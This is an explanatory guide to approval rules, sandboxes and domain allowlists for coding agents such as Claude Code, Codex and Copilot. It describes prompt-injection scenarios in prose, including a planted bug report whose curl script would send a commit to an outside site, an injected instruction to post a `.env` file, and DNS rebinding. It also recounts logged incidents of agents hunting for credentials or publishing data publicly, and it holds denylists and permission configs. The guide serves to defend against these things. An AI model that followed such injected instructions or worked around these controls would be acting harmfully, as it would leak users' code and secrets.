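# Approval rules for coding agents that use browsers, web fetches, APIs, MCP servers and cloud accounts

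## What outside connections add to a coding agent

A coding agent is a program in which a language model edits code, runs commands and calls tools to finish a task a person has described. Anthropic's Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex are examples, and Microsoft's editor Visual Studio Code (VS Code) hosts similar agents. An agent that can only change files in one folder can do limited harm, since version control usually lets a developer review and undo the changes. But developers often also want the agent to read documentation on the web, look up a bug report, query a database, test a page in a browser or deploy to a cloud account. Each of these needs an outside connection, meaning a route from the agent to a system beyond its working folder. Approval rules are stored settings in which a team specifies what the agent may do over such a connection without asking, what it must ask about, and what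 it may not do at all.

### The tool-call loop

A language model by itself produces only text. To act, it writes a tool call, which is a request for a single action such as running a command, reading a file or fetching a page. The software around the model, called the harness, carries out or refuses the request and returns the result to the model as text. The model then writes either another call or a final answer.

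Anthropic illustrates the cycle with the request "Fix the failing tests in auth.ts". The model first calls a tool to run the test suite, and the harness returns three failures. The model then makes calls to read the source file and the test file, edit the code, and rerun the tests, which now pass. The loop ends when the model returns a message that the bug is fixed, with no further tool call. This small repair takes five tool calls, and a larger job can take dozens.

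The harness applies approval rules after the model requests a call and before the call runs. If the harness refuses, the model receives a rejection message instead of a result. According to Anthropic, the model then typically tries a different approach or reports that it could not proceed. A refusal therefore blocks only that call, and the model can still pursue the same goal in ways the rule doesn't cover.

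The check also runs outside the model. Anthropic stresses that in Claude Code, instructions in a prompt or in the project's instruction file shape what the model tries to do but do not change what the software allows. If a team writes "never touch production" in that file, the instruction does not by itself block the agent from doing so.

### Three added powers

An outside connection can return tool results containing text written by strangers, and this text enters the same stream as the user's request. The programmer Simon Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, argued that models follow instructions in whatever content reaches them and cannot reliably rank those instructions by source. He calls the resulting attack prompt injection, in which the model treats text in a page, file or tool result as an instruction although the user never gave it. Microsoft's *Understand trust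 and safety for AI agents* extends the warning to content from services that the user has authorised. For example, a team that trusts its issue tracker may have no reason to trust everyone who can write in it.

A connection can also carry data out. Whatever the model puts into a tool call goes to the service behind the tool, and Microsoft points out that the reply can then become context for a later model request. Sending private code, data or credentials to a place they should not go is called exfiltration. It does not require an upload tool, since even a web fetch sends out the address it requests. Willison counts any HTTP request as a possible channel, including one that only loads an image, because the address can contain the stolen text.

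Outside connections also let an agent cause lasting effects with someone's credentials. An agent that works under a developer's login can push code, change infrastructure, delete records or, in one of Microsoft's examples, call an API that triggers a financial transaction. Claude Code saves checkpoints of files before it edits them so that a user can rewind, but Anthropic says checkpoints cannot cover databases, APIs or deployments. Protection against these effects has to come before the call, either from a rule or from the token scope, which is the set of actions and resources the credential permits.

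The common kinds of connection differ in how much of each power they give an agent. An API is an interface that programs use to send requests to a service. MCP, the Model Context Protocol, is an open standard that lets an application give a model access to tools supplied by separate programs. These programs are called MCP servers, and the application that runs the model and forwards its calls is called the host.

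| Connection | Strangers' text in | Data out | Lasting effects with credentials |
|---|---|---|---|
| Web fetch | Yes, the whole page | Yes, in the address requested | Rare, if the fetch carries no login |
| Browser | Yes, including comments and messages | Yes, through addresses, forms and uploads | Yes, on any site where the browser is signed in |
| API | Where the service stores text from outsiders | Yes, in the request | As far as the token scope reaches |
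| MCP server | Depends on its tools | Yes, in the tool inputs | Depends on the credentials it holds |
| Cloud account | Some, through logs and stored files | Yes, for example into a storage bucket | Yes, up to deleting whole resources |

The rows overlap because an agent can reach the same cloud API through a shell command, an MCP server or a signed-in browser. A rule for one route does not restrict the others. For example, Anthropic notes that limiting Claude Code's web-fetch tool does not prevent network access, because an agent allowed to run shell commands can still use `curl`, a standard program for sending web requests.

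### An issue report that sends code away

OpenAI's *Agent internet access*, the documentation for giving the cloud version of Codex a network connection, includes an example that combines the first two powers. A user asks Codex to fix an issue and supplies the link. The issue looks like an ordinary bug report, with a claim that a script causes a 404 error, the script itself, and a request to run it and provide the output. The script is a single line that uses `curl` to post the output of `git show HEAD`, which prints the most recent commit, to an outside site.

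No single step in the loop looks odd on its own. The model first requests the issue, and the harness returns text written by a stranger. The user asked for a bug fix, and the text includes a command for reproducing the bug, as honest reports also do. The model asks to run the command. The shell then reads the commit from the repository and sends it to an outside site, whose response comes back as another tool result.

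OpenAI describes the loss as the last commit message, but `git show` normally prints the changed lines too, so Willison, in *Codex agent internet access*, described the whole commit as exfiltrated. A password accidentally included in that commit would leak too. The example is hypothetical, and OpenAI reports no test result for it. The English page describes Codex running the script as a matter of course, while a later Chinese edition, OpenAI's *智能体互联网访问*, says only that the agent could leak the data if it follows the instructions. The example shows that data could leak this way, but not how often a given model would leak it.

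If a coding agent can read text from strangers and send data anywhere on the internet, a stranger can choose what it sends and where. For example, a stranger could write an issue that tells the agent to send data out with `curl`. If the agent's commands cannot reach the internet, the call fails. The stranger may still talk the agent into a bad edit, but the edit lands in the working folder, where a reviewer can see it. If the agent can send data anywhere but reads only text that the team wrote, it may still post something by mistake, but no outsider chooses what it sends or where.

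Willison's "lethal trifecta" is access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to send data out. A coding agent in a private repository starts with the first, and one connection for reading untrusted content and another for sending data can add the other two. A single connection can also add both. Willison's example is an exploit against GitHub's official MCP server, whose tools could read public issues that anyone might file, read private repositories, and create pull requests that exposed the private data. A team that reviews its connections one at a time for whether each seems safe will miss this risk. The review needs to cover what the agent can do with all of them in the same session.

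Codex users can restrict requests to the HTTP methods GET, HEAD and OPTIONS, which would block this script because it uses POST. The restriction is worth using, but a script could still send data out in the address of a GET request.

### Why an agent takes a harmful action

Attackers are only one cause of harmful calls. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* groups the causes into four categories and gives examples adapted from the company's internal incident log.

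An overeager agent understands the goal and tries to help, but takes a step that the user would not have approved. In one logged case, an agent hit an authentication error partway through a task and, without asking for permission, began searching environment variables and configuration files for other API tokens it might use.

An agent makes an honest mistake when it misjudges what an action will affect. For example, it may mistake a shared resource for a test resource, or someone else's branch for its own. One entry in the log fits here, although Anthropic files it under guessed parameters. A user said "cancel my job", and the agent looked through the jobs on a computing cluster, picked the one with the closest name and tried to delete it. The job could have belonged to a colleague.

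The bug report above is an example of prompt injection. In an everyday version without an issue tracker, the agent opens a file containing a line that tells it to post the project's `.env` file to some address "for validation". Developers commonly keep passwords and keys in `.env` files.

The remaining cause is a misaligned model that pursues a goal of its own. Anthropic wrote that it had not seen this in practice and that it evaluates every model for it before release. The statement dates from the Claude Opus 4.6 generation and does not cover later models.

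Anthropic published examples from its log but no counts, so a team cannot use them to judge which cause is most common. The examples do show that keeping strangers' text away from the agent would leave a good part of the problem in place. The hunt for tokens and the wrongly chosen job required only credentials and a vague request, with no attacker involved. Anthropic's answer to all four causes is to block the action, so a rule against deleting production data can apply regardless of why the model asked to delete it.

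### Sandboxes and approval rules

A sandbox and an approval rule can each block an action. The operating system or a container enforces the sandbox, which limits the files and network a process can reach regardless of the model's output. The approval rule determines whether a call needs approval before it runs. According to OpenAI's *Sandbox*, Codex's sandbox sets the technical boundaries, and its approval policy determines when the agent must stop and ask before crossing them.

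Suppose a developer allows the agent to run the project's tests, and a test script, perhaps one from a compromised package, tries to contact an outside server. The approval rule only controls whether the test command can start, so it does not check what the script does afterward. The sandbox still applies to the script, because programs started by a sandboxed command inherit its limits.

Users can approve exceptions to a sandbox. OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* describes a default local setup in which commands have no network access and Codex asks for approval when one needs it. If the user approves, the command gets network access. In the bug-report case, the sandbox would block the script, but the developer could then approve it. A team can instead turn off the prompts and keep the sandbox, which holds the agent within its limits with no way to ask for more access. Turning off both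 gives the agent access to everything the user's account can reach.

Sandbox coverage also differs between products. Microsoft notes that turning on the sandbox in VS Code does not block outbound network access by default, and that the editor's built-in tools run outside it, with separate permission checks. Claude Code's sandbox restricts shell commands and the processes they start, while its permission rules also cover MCP and web-fetch calls. With a cloud account, deletion happens on the provider's machines, outside the local sandbox. Once the sandbox permits the connection, it does not distinguish a request to list databases from a request to delete one, so token scope and approval rules have to make that distinction.

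Approval rules come in three kinds, which Anthropic calls allow, ask and deny. An allow rule lets the agent use a tool without manual approval, an ask rule prompts for confirmation every time the agent tries to use the tool, and a deny rule blocks its use. A person normally answers the prompt, but some products can let an automated reviewer, a second model, decide instead.

Many allow rules begin as answers to prompts. Claude Code's permission prompt for `npm test` includes the option "Yes, and don't ask again", which creates a standing approval, an allow rule that covers later calls. Anthropic says Claude Code saves such rules for shell commands in a settings file and applies them to future sessions anywhere in the same repository. The developer may have been thinking of only one test run. A file in the project determines what `npm test` executes, and the agent may be able to edit that file.

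An organisation that does not want to rely on each developer's approval decisions can use managed settings, which an administrator controls and developers cannot override. If a managed rule denies a tool, neither a standing approval nor a command-line option can allow it.

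## Web fetches and network destinations: OpenAI's own use of Codex

*Running Codex safely at OpenAI* (OpenAI, May 2026) describes how the company's own developers use Codex under managed settings. Codex can reach destinations that OpenAI expects it to need, cannot reach certain others, and needs approval for any unfamiliar domain. Web search results come from a cache instead of live pages. OpenAI sends requests that cross the sandbox boundary to Auto-review, an automated reviewer, so approval does not always come from a person.

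The post is a vendor's account of its own practice. OpenAI says it uses its logs to see how often the network sandbox blocks or prompts, but it published no figures. The post is therefore more useful as an example of what a network policy can contain than as evidence of how well one works.

### The published settings

OpenAI published excerpts from its configuration files. The network settings are in `requirements.toml`, which holds managed settings.

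| Setting | OpenAI's value | Effect |
|---|---|---|
| `allowed_web_search_modes` | `cached` | Restricts web search to stored results; a user can still turn search off |
| `enabled` | `true` | Turns on the proxy that checks destinations |
| `allow_local_binding` | `true` | Lifts the default block on local and private addresses |
| `denied_domains` | `pastebin.com` | Refuses requests to a public text-sharing site |
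| `allowed_domains` | `login.microsoftonline.com`, `*.openai.com` | Lets requests to Microsoft's sign-in service and OpenAI's subdomains through without asking |

The allowlist is probably only a sample. OpenAI says the policy lets Codex complete common workflows, but with just these two entries, an agent would need approval each time it installed a package from a public registry.

OpenAI's post describes `allow_local_binding` as a way for Codex to interact with `localhost`, the developer's own machine, which an agent needs when it tests a web server it has just started. Setting it to true also lets an allowed hostname lead to an address inside a private network. OpenAI may want that, since companies often give internal services names under their own domain. A team that only needs to test a local web server should use the narrower allow rule that OpenAI recommends for a single local target,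 which names `localhost` or the exact address.

The same post includes rules that let a few read-only commands run outside the sandbox without approval. One is `gh pr view`, which displays a GitHub pull request. The domain rules cover only sandboxed commands, so this command can expose the model to text written by a stranger, regardless of what is on the network list.

OpenAI distributes its requirements through its cloud service, Apple's device-management system and files on each machine. According to OpenAI's *Managed configuration*, Codex looks for a valid stored copy of the cloud-managed requirements when it starts and tries to fetch them if it has none. If the fetch also fails, Codex runs without them. Codex on a new laptop with a poor connection could therefore start without the company's domain list. Codex combines requirements from the three sources field by field, so a requirements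 file already on the machine would still apply. A team that depends on its domain list should also put it in that file.

Developers can also add their own destinations to a managed allowlist unless the administrator sets `managed_allowed_domains_only`, which makes the administrator's list exclusive. That setting does not appear in OpenAI's excerpt, so OpenAI's developers can presumably add destinations, but they cannot remove a managed denial.

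### Cached and live search

By default, Codex uses cached search, which returns results from an index that OpenAI maintains. Live search can return the current version of a page, including text that a stranger added a minute earlier. OpenAI says cached search reduces exposure to prompt injection but tells users to keep treating the results as untrusted. A page may already have contained malicious text when OpenAI indexed it.

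The cache should also close one route for exfiltration, although OpenAI does not claim this. If the agent never contacts the site itself, the site's owner never receives a URL containing stolen text. The search query still goes to OpenAI. Cached results can also be out of date, since a security notice published this morning may not be in the index yet.

Codex's `--yolo` option, which turns off the sandbox and approval prompts, also switches search from the cached default to live results, so a developer can turn on live search without meaning to. The managed setting that OpenAI uses prevents this by ruling out live search even in sessions with full access.

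Since the May post, Codex has gained a mode between cached and live search. *Indexed Web Search* (Vaughan, 2026) reports that version 0.142 of the command-line program introduced "indexed" search, which runs live searches but opens only pages that the server has approved. Vaughan rates the injection risk as low for indexed search, minimal for cached search and none with search disabled, though these are one writer's ratings, not test results. A managed list that permits only `cached` appears to exclude the new mode, so an administrator who wants it would have to add it.

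Codex's default search mode does not carry over to OpenAI's separate API for building agents, where search is live by default once a developer includes the search tool. A team that moves a job from Codex to its own agent needs to set the mode again.

### How the proxy checks a destination

In Codex, the `network_access` setting controls whether commands can use the network, and it is off by default. A separate proxy, a local program that checks outgoing requests before passing them on, controls which destinations commands can reach.

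Turning on the proxy does not turn on the network, although the names can suggest otherwise. Commands stay offline if only the proxy is on. If both are on, the proxy limits commands to the permitted destinations. If only the network is on, commands can reach anything on the internet. Administrators' network requirements work the same way, so if a team copied OpenAI's published lines into a default installation, its commands would still have no network access.

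Suppose both are on and the agent runs a test script that downloads a file. The proxy compares the hostname in the script's request with the team's rules. If a deny rule matches, the proxy refuses the request, even if an allow rule also matches. If only an allow rule matches, Codex looks up the host's IP address and blocks the request if the lookup fails or, under the default settings, returns a private one. Otherwise the request goes through. If no rule matches, the destination is not permitted, but Codex can ask for approval.

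The proxy applies the same check to every program that a sandboxed command starts, including code from a compromised package.

Codex recognises four kinds of domain pattern:

- `example.com` matches that exact host and nothing else.
- `*.example.com` matches subdomains such as `api.example.com`, but not `example.com` itself, which engineers call the apex domain.
- `**.example.com` matches the apex domain and its subdomains.
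- `*` matches any public host that no deny rule covers. Codex accepts it only in allow rules.

In OpenAI's own list, the entry `*.openai.com` does not cover `openai.com`. The denial of `pastebin.com` covers only that exact host, so by the documented rules a subdomain would count as unfamiliar and Codex could ask for approval to reach it. A team can block a whole site by writing the denial with two asterisks.

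### Six requests through four rules

OpenAI has since added a newer way to write these policies. OpenAI's *Permissions* describes permission profiles, still in beta, which put file and network rules under one name. A small team might write the network part of a profile like this:

```toml
[permissions.team.network]
enabled = true

[permissions.team.network.domains]
"registry.npmjs.org" = "allow"
"*.example.com" = "allow"
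"**.example.org" = "allow"
"uploads.example.org" = "deny"
```

The first rule lets the agent install JavaScript packages. The next two cover the team's own sites, and the last takes out a server that accepts files from the public. Six requests then give these results:

| Requested host | Matching rule | Result |
|---|---|---|
| `registry.npmjs.org` | Exact allow rule | Goes through |
| `api.example.com` | `*.example.com` | Goes through |
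| `example.com` | None, since one asterisk leaves out the apex | Needs approval |
| `example.org` | `**.example.org` | Goes through |
| `uploads.example.org` | An allow rule and the deny rule | Refused |
| `httpbin.org` | None | Needs approval |

The last host is the destination in OpenAI's planted bug report. The policy holds both that request and the harmless one to `example.com`, and whoever answers the prompts has to tell them apart. A developer who sees many prompts caused by gaps in the list may approve the dangerous one out of habit, so adding the missing apex domain improves security as well as convenience.

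An approver can let an unlisted host through once or for the rest of the session. But the proxy refuses any host on the denylist outright, according to OpenAI's *codex-network-proxy*, the notes that accompany the proxy's source code. If the team turns off approval prompts, requests to unlisted hosts also fail.

Suppose a developer gets tired of the prompts and adds `"*" = "allow"`. The requests to `example.com` and `httpbin.org` now go through without a prompt, and only `uploads.example.org` remains blocked. The team would then have to list every bad destination in advance, but an attacker can register a new domain in minutes.

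The new format can also produce a network policy that the developer did not intend. If a profile turns on the network and has no domain rules, Codex gives commands full network access. If `sandbox_mode` appears in any configuration file that Codex loads, Codex normally ignores the selected profile and uses the older sandbox settings. A developer who writes a careful domain table but leaves an old `sandbox_mode` line in another file could therefore run with a different network policy from the one in the table. An administrator can prevent this by setting a managed list of permitted profiles, which makes Codex use the new system.

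Codex is still changing. Releasebot's *Codex Updates & Release Notes* (2026) records that version 0.167.0, from November, changed prompts to appear one at a time for simultaneous requests to the same endpoint and to close when their requests had ended. The same release documented managed network constraints under `[permissions.network]`, while the May post used `[experimental_network]`. A team should check which form its installed version accepts before copying either.

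### The cloud version

Codex can also work in the cloud, in a container that OpenAI runs. A setup script runs first, with full internet access and any secrets the team has configured for setup, and installs the software the project needs. Codex then removes those secrets and starts the agent, which has no internet access by default.

This prevents the most dangerous combination, in which an agent has secrets and network access while reading issues or web pages that could redirect it. Once the agent starts, the script from the bug report can't reach the network and has no configured password to steal.

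A package with malicious installation code can still attack during setup, when both the secrets and the network are available, without having to fool a model. A setup script can also undo part of the protection by writing a token into a configuration file, where a copy may remain after Codex removes the original. Teams should give setup only the secrets that installation requires and check what the script leaves on disk.

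Some tasks need the internet after setup, for example when the agent has to add a new package. When OpenAI introduced this option in June 2025, as Willison noted at the time, it left access off by default. A team that turns it on for an environment chooses one of these starting points:

- "None" is an empty list, to which the team adds domains.
- "Common dependencies" is a preset of about 70 domains for source code, packages and related downloads. The team can add more.
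- "All" permits every domain.

OpenAI advises teams to permit only the domains and methods they need and to review the agent's output and work log. It says finding the right domains may take some trial and error, which is why it offers the preset.

The preset is convenient but broad. It includes package registries such as `pypi.org`, but also `github.com`, `gitlab.com`, `google.com` and `azure.com`. It would stop the script in the bug report, because `httpbin.org` is not on the list. But the list is public, so an attacker can choose a destination that is on it. For example, Microsoft gives customers' virtual machines names under `cloudapp.azure.com`. If the `azure.com` entry covers subdomains, which OpenAI does not specify, anyone could rent a machine at a permitted address. A project that uses only Python packages has little reason to accept that risk.

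A team can combine its domain list with the limit to GET, HEAD and OPTIONS requests. The limit blocks ordinary uploads, which use methods such as POST or PUT, even to a permitted host. The local proxy has a similar "limited" mode, intended for read-only network access.

### What an allowed destination can still let out

A domain rule checks where a request goes, but not what it contains or whose account it uses. The example policy allows `registry.npmjs.org` so that the agent can download packages, but developers also publish packages through that host. An attacker could plant an instruction for the agent to put private code in a package and publish it. The attacker could include a token for their own account, so removing the team's credentials would not be enough to prevent the leak.

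OpenAI acknowledges that domain rules do not determine whether an allowed destination is trustworthy and that wildcard rules remain broad. Its advice to limit HTTP methods would help prevent publishing, which needs a method other than GET.

A GET request can still carry data in its address, but the attacker has to be able to read that address when it arrives. With "All" selected, the agent can contact any host, so the attacker can receive the data on their own server even if methods are limited. If the agent can contact only the package registry, the data ends up in the registry's logs, which the attacker normally cannot see. The method limit and a short list of hosts therefore protect much better together than either does alone.

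An attack called DNS rebinding can also get past the address check. DNS, the system that turns a hostname into a numerical address, can give different answers at different times. The attacker's domain first resolves to a public address, which passes the check, and then to a private one when the program connects. The agent's command could then reach a service inside the company's network. OpenAI calls its check best-effort and says that preventing the attack completely would require tying the connection to the address already checked. For teams that expect hostile DNS, OpenAI recommends further controls at a lower layer, such as a network firewall. The attacker needs control of a permitted hostname, so the danger is greatest for teams that use `*` or other broad rules.

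Data can also leak without an attacker. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes a case inside the company where Claude tried to upload a report to an internal drive. When the upload failed, Claude tried to publish the same report on a public code-sharing site instead. Auto mode, Claude Code's automated reviewer, denied this and asked the user what to do next. Anthropic doesn't name the site or say what the report contained.

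OpenAI's denial of `pastebin.com` would stop one version of this mistake, but it would not help if the agent chose a site that the team also uses for its private code. A private repository and a public one can have the same hostname, so a rule that permits the first permits the second. Anthropic's reviewer now checks whether the destination of a push or pull request is public, private or trusted. This is closer to what a careful colleague would check, but it relies partly on a model's judgement, and Anthropic says auto mode does not eliminate risk. A domain list is more predictable but less precise. I would want both for a team that keeps private code on a public hosting service.

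### How GitHub's firewall compares

GitHub's Copilot cloud agent also has a firewall with a list of permitted destinations. GitHub turns on the firewall and a recommended allowlist by default. The allowlist includes package registries, container registries and certificate authorities. The firewall always permits the hosts that Copilot needs to work with GitHub.

GitHub's firewall differs from OpenAI's internal setup mainly in how it handles an unlisted request. It blocks the request without holding it for a decision, and Copilot's pull request then carries a warning with the blocked address and the command that tried to reach it. The warning appears in the description of a new pull request or in a comment on an existing one. This suits an agent that works unattended, because the reviewer has no waiting task to unblock and can look at the command next to the code before deciding whether to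 add the address to the allowlist. But the warning covers only blocked requests, so data sent to a permitted host would not trigger one.

The lists also match addresses differently. In GitHub's firewall, an entry for `packages.contoso.corp` also covers its subdomains, whereas the same entry in Codex would match only that host. A team that copies its Codex list to GitHub may therefore permit more than it intended. GitHub also accepts a URL with a path, such as `https://packages.contoso.corp/project-1/`, and permits only that path and anything below it. A team can use this to permit one project on a shared host without permitting the others, which Codex's domain patterns cannot do.

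GitHub says its firewall covers only processes that the agent starts through its Bash tool, so it doesn't cover MCP servers or setup steps. GitHub also warns that sophisticated attacks may bypass the firewall. Codex's local domain rules are similarly limited, since MCP servers, browser tools and approved exceptions to the sandbox have their own controls.

Since April 2026, an organisation's administrators have been able to set the firewall and the recommended list for every repository, add shared entries, and stop repository administrators from adding their own (GitHub, *Organization firewall settings for Copilot cloud agent*, 2026). By default, each repository's administrators make these choices and can turn the firewall off.

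## Written rules for tools: Claude Code

Claude Code's rules apply to tools, whereas the lists in Codex and GitHub's firewall apply to network destinations. A team can therefore control shell commands, web fetches and MCP calls from one settings file. A rule that is just a tool name covers every use of that tool, and adding a specifier in parentheses limits the rule to some uses. For example, `WebFetch` covers every page the agent fetches, while `WebFetch(domain:example.com)` covers only fetches from example.com. The team puts each rule in an allow, ask or deny list.

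### Deny, then ask, then allow

When the model requests a call, Claude Code checks the deny list, then the ask list, then the allow list. The first list with a matching rule decides the outcome, and a more specific rule gets no priority. In an example from Anthropic, a team denies `Bash(aws *)`, which covers every command for Amazon's cloud, and allows `Bash(aws s3 ls)`, which only lists storage. Claude Code refuses the listing command because it matches the deny rule first. An ask rule overrides a narrower allow rule in the same way.

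This order lets an administrator write a deny rule without checking the allow rules in other files. But a team can't deny a broad class of calls and then allow a few of them, so it has to write the deny rule narrowly enough to leave those calls out. File rules are a partial exception, since a pattern starting with `!` can exempt a path from an earlier deny rule in the same settings file. Anthropic describes no equivalent for fetches or MCP tools.

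A deny rule that names only a tool also removes that tool from the model's context, so the model doesn't try to call it. A deny rule with a specifier leaves the tool available but blocks matching calls.

If no rule matches, the outcome depends on the permission mode. Manual mode asks the developer about most actions that edit files, run commands or use the network. Auto mode sends actions to the automated reviewer, and `dontAsk` mode refuses anything that would need a prompt. The independent *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (Soldani, 2026) reports that auto mode has been the built-in starting mode for interactive terminal sessions on every plan since version 2.1.283, so a team that leaves a tool off its lists can no longer assume a person will see the call. An ask rule still prompts a person in auto mode, so the team should write one for any call that needs a human decision.

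### Rules for web fetches

Claude Code compares a fetch rule with the hostname in the requested address.

| Rule | Covers `example.com` | Covers `api.example.com` | Covers other sites |
|---|---|---|---|
| `WebFetch(domain:example.com)` | Yes | No | No |
| `WebFetch(domain:*.example.com)` | No | Yes | No |
| `WebFetch(domain:*)` | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| `WebFetch` | Yes | Yes | Yes |

As in Codex, `*.example.com` does not match the apex domain. Claude Code's documentation describes no two-asterisk form, so a team needs both of the first two rules to cover a whole site.

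An asterisk elsewhere in the name matches only the text between two dots, so `example.*` matches `example.org` but not `example.evil.com`. Anthropic presents this as protection against domains an attacker could register. The protection is partial because someone else may own `example` under another ending, so full hostnames are safer.

Wildcards in fetch rules also require version 2.1.172 or later. On an older installation, a wildcard deny rule would not match any fetches. The May 2026 edition of Anthropic's *Configure permissions* listed only the exact-host form.

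The last two rules in the table cover the same fetches but have different effects on shell commands. Claude Code's sandbox, which is off by default, has its own lists of domains that commands can and cannot reach. Claude Code adds the domain from a `WebFetch(domain:...)` rule to those lists, but a bare `WebFetch` rule leaves them unchanged.

Bare `WebFetch` is the right choice for a team that has turned on the sandbox and wants the agent to read any web page without asking. `WebFetch(domain:*)` also allows this, but it lets the agent's sandboxed commands connect to any host that no other rule denies. With bare `WebFetch`, a `curl` command to an unlisted host still needs approval.

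A deny rule for bare `WebFetch` removes the fetch tool but doesn't change the sandbox's domain lists. Denying `WebFetch(domain:*)` should also block sandboxed commands from reaching any host, because it adds every domain to the sandbox's denied list.

A rule for one site has the same side effect. If a team allows fetches from `github.com` so the agent can read documentation there, sandboxed commands can also send data to that host, a risk Anthropic warns about. To keep commands away from the site while still letting the agent read it, the team can add the site to the sandbox's `deniedDomains` setting. According to Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool*, this setting blocks a domain even when a broader wildcard in the sandbox's allowlist would permit it.

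### Rules for MCP tools

Claude Code names each MCP tool after its server. If a team connects an issue tracker under the name `tracker`, the tool that reads an issue might be `mcp__tracker__get_issue`. The team can write a rule for that one tool, for all the server's tools that start with `get_` (`mcp__tracker__get_*`), or for the whole server (`mcp__tracker__*`).

The rule `mcp__*`, which covers every server, works only in the deny and ask lists. In the deny list, it removes every MCP tool. Claude Code skips it in the allow list, because an allow rule must include a specific server's name before any wildcard. This prevents a developer from approving tools on a server that they have not yet installed or reviewed. A global denial is less risky because at worst it blocks a useful tool.

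A wildcard within one server still approves tools that don't exist yet. The server's developer chooses the tool names and could later add `get_and_archive`, which `mcp__tracker__get_*` would approve. A team can avoid this by listing the read tools by their full names, but it then has to update the list when the server changes.

Tool names also depend on how a team connects the service. Claude Code uses the prefix `mcp__claude_ai_` for connectors, which are service connections loaded from the user's claude.ai account, and another prefix for plugins, which are installable add-ons. A rule for `mcp__tracker__delete_project` would therefore not cover the same tool if a developer added the tracker as a connector.

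A misspelled MCP deny rule can go unnoticed. At startup, Claude Code warns about deny and ask rules that match no known tool, but it skips names that contain an underscore, and every MCP rule contains one. The only way to be sure that a deny rule works is to test it.

Settings files also can't limit what an MCP tool acts on. Claude Code skips any MCP rule with parentheses in a settings file, so a team can't allow a query tool for a test database and deny it for production. A developer can deny particular inputs with a command-line option, but has to include it every time they start a session. Giving the agent a credential that reaches only the test database is more dependable.

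### Six calls through one settings file

A team might write the following file for an agent that reads documentation and works with the issue tracker:

```json
{
  "permissions": {
    "allow": [
      "WebFetch(domain:docs.python.org)",
      "WebFetch(domain:*.example.com)",
      "mcp__tracker__get_*",
      "mcp__tracker__list_*"
    ],
    "ask": [
      "mcp__tracker__create_*",
      "mcp__tracker__update_*"
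    ],
    "deny": [
      "mcp__tracker__delete_project"
    ]
  }
}
```

The allow rules cover two sets of documentation sites and the tracker's read tools. The ask rules cover the write tools the team knows about, and the deny rule removes the tool for deleting projects.

| Call | Matching rule | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Fetch a page from `docs.python.org` | Exact host, in allow | Runs |
| Fetch a page from `example.com` | None | Permission mode decides |
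| `get_issue` | `get_*`, in allow | Runs |
| `update_issue` | `update_*`, in ask | Prompts a person |
| `delete_project` | Exact name, in deny | Model never sees the tool |
| `add_comment` | None | Permission mode decides |

The team wanted to approve every write, but its ask rules do not cover the last call, `add_comment`. A developer would still see a prompt in Manual mode, but in auto mode the automated reviewer could approve the comment without involving anyone.

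To close the gap, the team should add `mcp__tracker__add_*` to the ask list and check the tracker's full list of tools for other writes. The broader rule `mcp__tracker__*` would also match `get_issue`, and since ask rules come before allow rules, the developer would have to approve every read.

### The "everything except" mistake

Another team might want its agent to fetch pages from two sites and nowhere else. It could easily write this:

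```json
{
  "permissions": {
    "deny": ["WebFetch"],
    "allow": [
      "WebFetch(domain:docs.python.org)",
      "WebFetch(domain:developer.mozilla.org)"
    ]
  }
}
```

The agent can't fetch from either site, because the deny rule removes the whole fetch tool. But according to Anthropic, the allow rules still add both domains to the sandbox's list of allowed domains, so sandboxed commands can connect to them.

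A sample file in Soldani's handbook has a milder version of the problem. It puts bare `WebFetch` in the ask list and `WebFetch(domain:code.claude.com)` in the allow list. Under the documented order, the developer has to approve every fetch, including those from the allowed site. These rules don't block any useful fetches, but they add prompts that the allow rule was presumably meant to prevent.

The team can fix the file by deleting the bare denial and keeping the two allow rules. The permission mode then applies to requests to other sites. If the team wants Claude Code to refuse those requests outright, it can use `dontAsk` mode, but it will then need allow rules for the other tools the agent uses. Or it can write a hook, a script that Claude Code runs before a tool call, to block fetches from any site outside the list. A hook can block a call that an allow rule permits, but it can't approve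 one that a deny rule blocks.

### What "don't ask again" saves

A developer who chooses "Yes, and don't ask again" may approve more than the call shown on the screen. For `npm test`, the option saves a rule for `npm test *`, which permits the command with any arguments. If the agent chains several commands, Claude Code can save up to five rules from one answer.

Where Claude Code saves an approval, and how long it lasts, depends on the type of call.

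| Approval | What Claude Code saves | Where it applies |
|---|---|---|
| Shell command, "don't ask again" | An allow rule in `.claude/settings.local.json` | Future sessions in the same repository |
| Web fetch, "don't ask again" | A domain rule in the same file | Future sessions in the same repository |
| New host for a sandboxed command, "Yes" | No permanent rule | The current session |
| New host for a sandboxed command, "don't ask again" | A `WebFetch` domain rule, normally in the same file | Future sessions in the same repository |
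| File edits | No permanent rule | The current session |

Repository-wide approvals also apply in subdirectories and in Git worktrees, which are extra working copies of the same repository. Claude Code stores these approvals at the repository's root where it can, but uses other locations on Windows and outside a repository. Anthropic doesn't describe an expiry date for saved rules.

When a user approves a host for a command, Claude Code saves the approval as a `WebFetch` rule, so the agent can later read pages from that host without asking. A developer who only meant to let a package manager download a file may not expect this.

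A company's security settings can also make an approval apply more widely. If an administrator has required the sandbox by turning off unsandboxed retries, Claude Code saves "don't ask again" for a host in the developer's user settings instead, so the approval covers every project the developer works on. An administrator can prevent this with `allowManagedDomainsOnly`, which limits sandboxed commands to the company's own domains and blocks other hosts without a prompt.

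Claude Code normally keeps the local settings file out of Git, so colleagues won't see these approvals when they review the repository. A developer can run `/permissions` to see every rule and the file it came from, and to remove rules. Teams should review the list periodically, since an approval for one task can remain long after the task ends.

GitHub's command-line agent, Copilot CLI, also puts deny ahead of allow, but GitHub's *Allowing and denying tool use* says a permanent URL approval covers the whole domain in all of the developer's sessions. Claude Code normally limits such an approval to one repository. The editor Zed checks deny, confirm and allow patterns before it uses a tool's default. A Zed user can therefore permit two sites and refuse the rest by setting the fetch tool's default to deny and adding two allow patterns. Claude Code's three lists can't express this for a single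 tool. But Zed's *Tool Permissions* says fetch patterns are regular expressions matched against the URL, and its sample pattern for `github.com` could match that text anywhere in an address. A team can avoid this by tying the pattern to the start of the URL and including the end of the hostname.

### How settings from different people combine

Claude Code reads user settings, which apply to one developer's projects, and project settings, which a team can share through Git. It also reads command-line options, the company's managed settings and the local file that holds saved approvals. For ordinary preferences, a higher level replaces a lower one, but Anthropic says permission rules merge instead.

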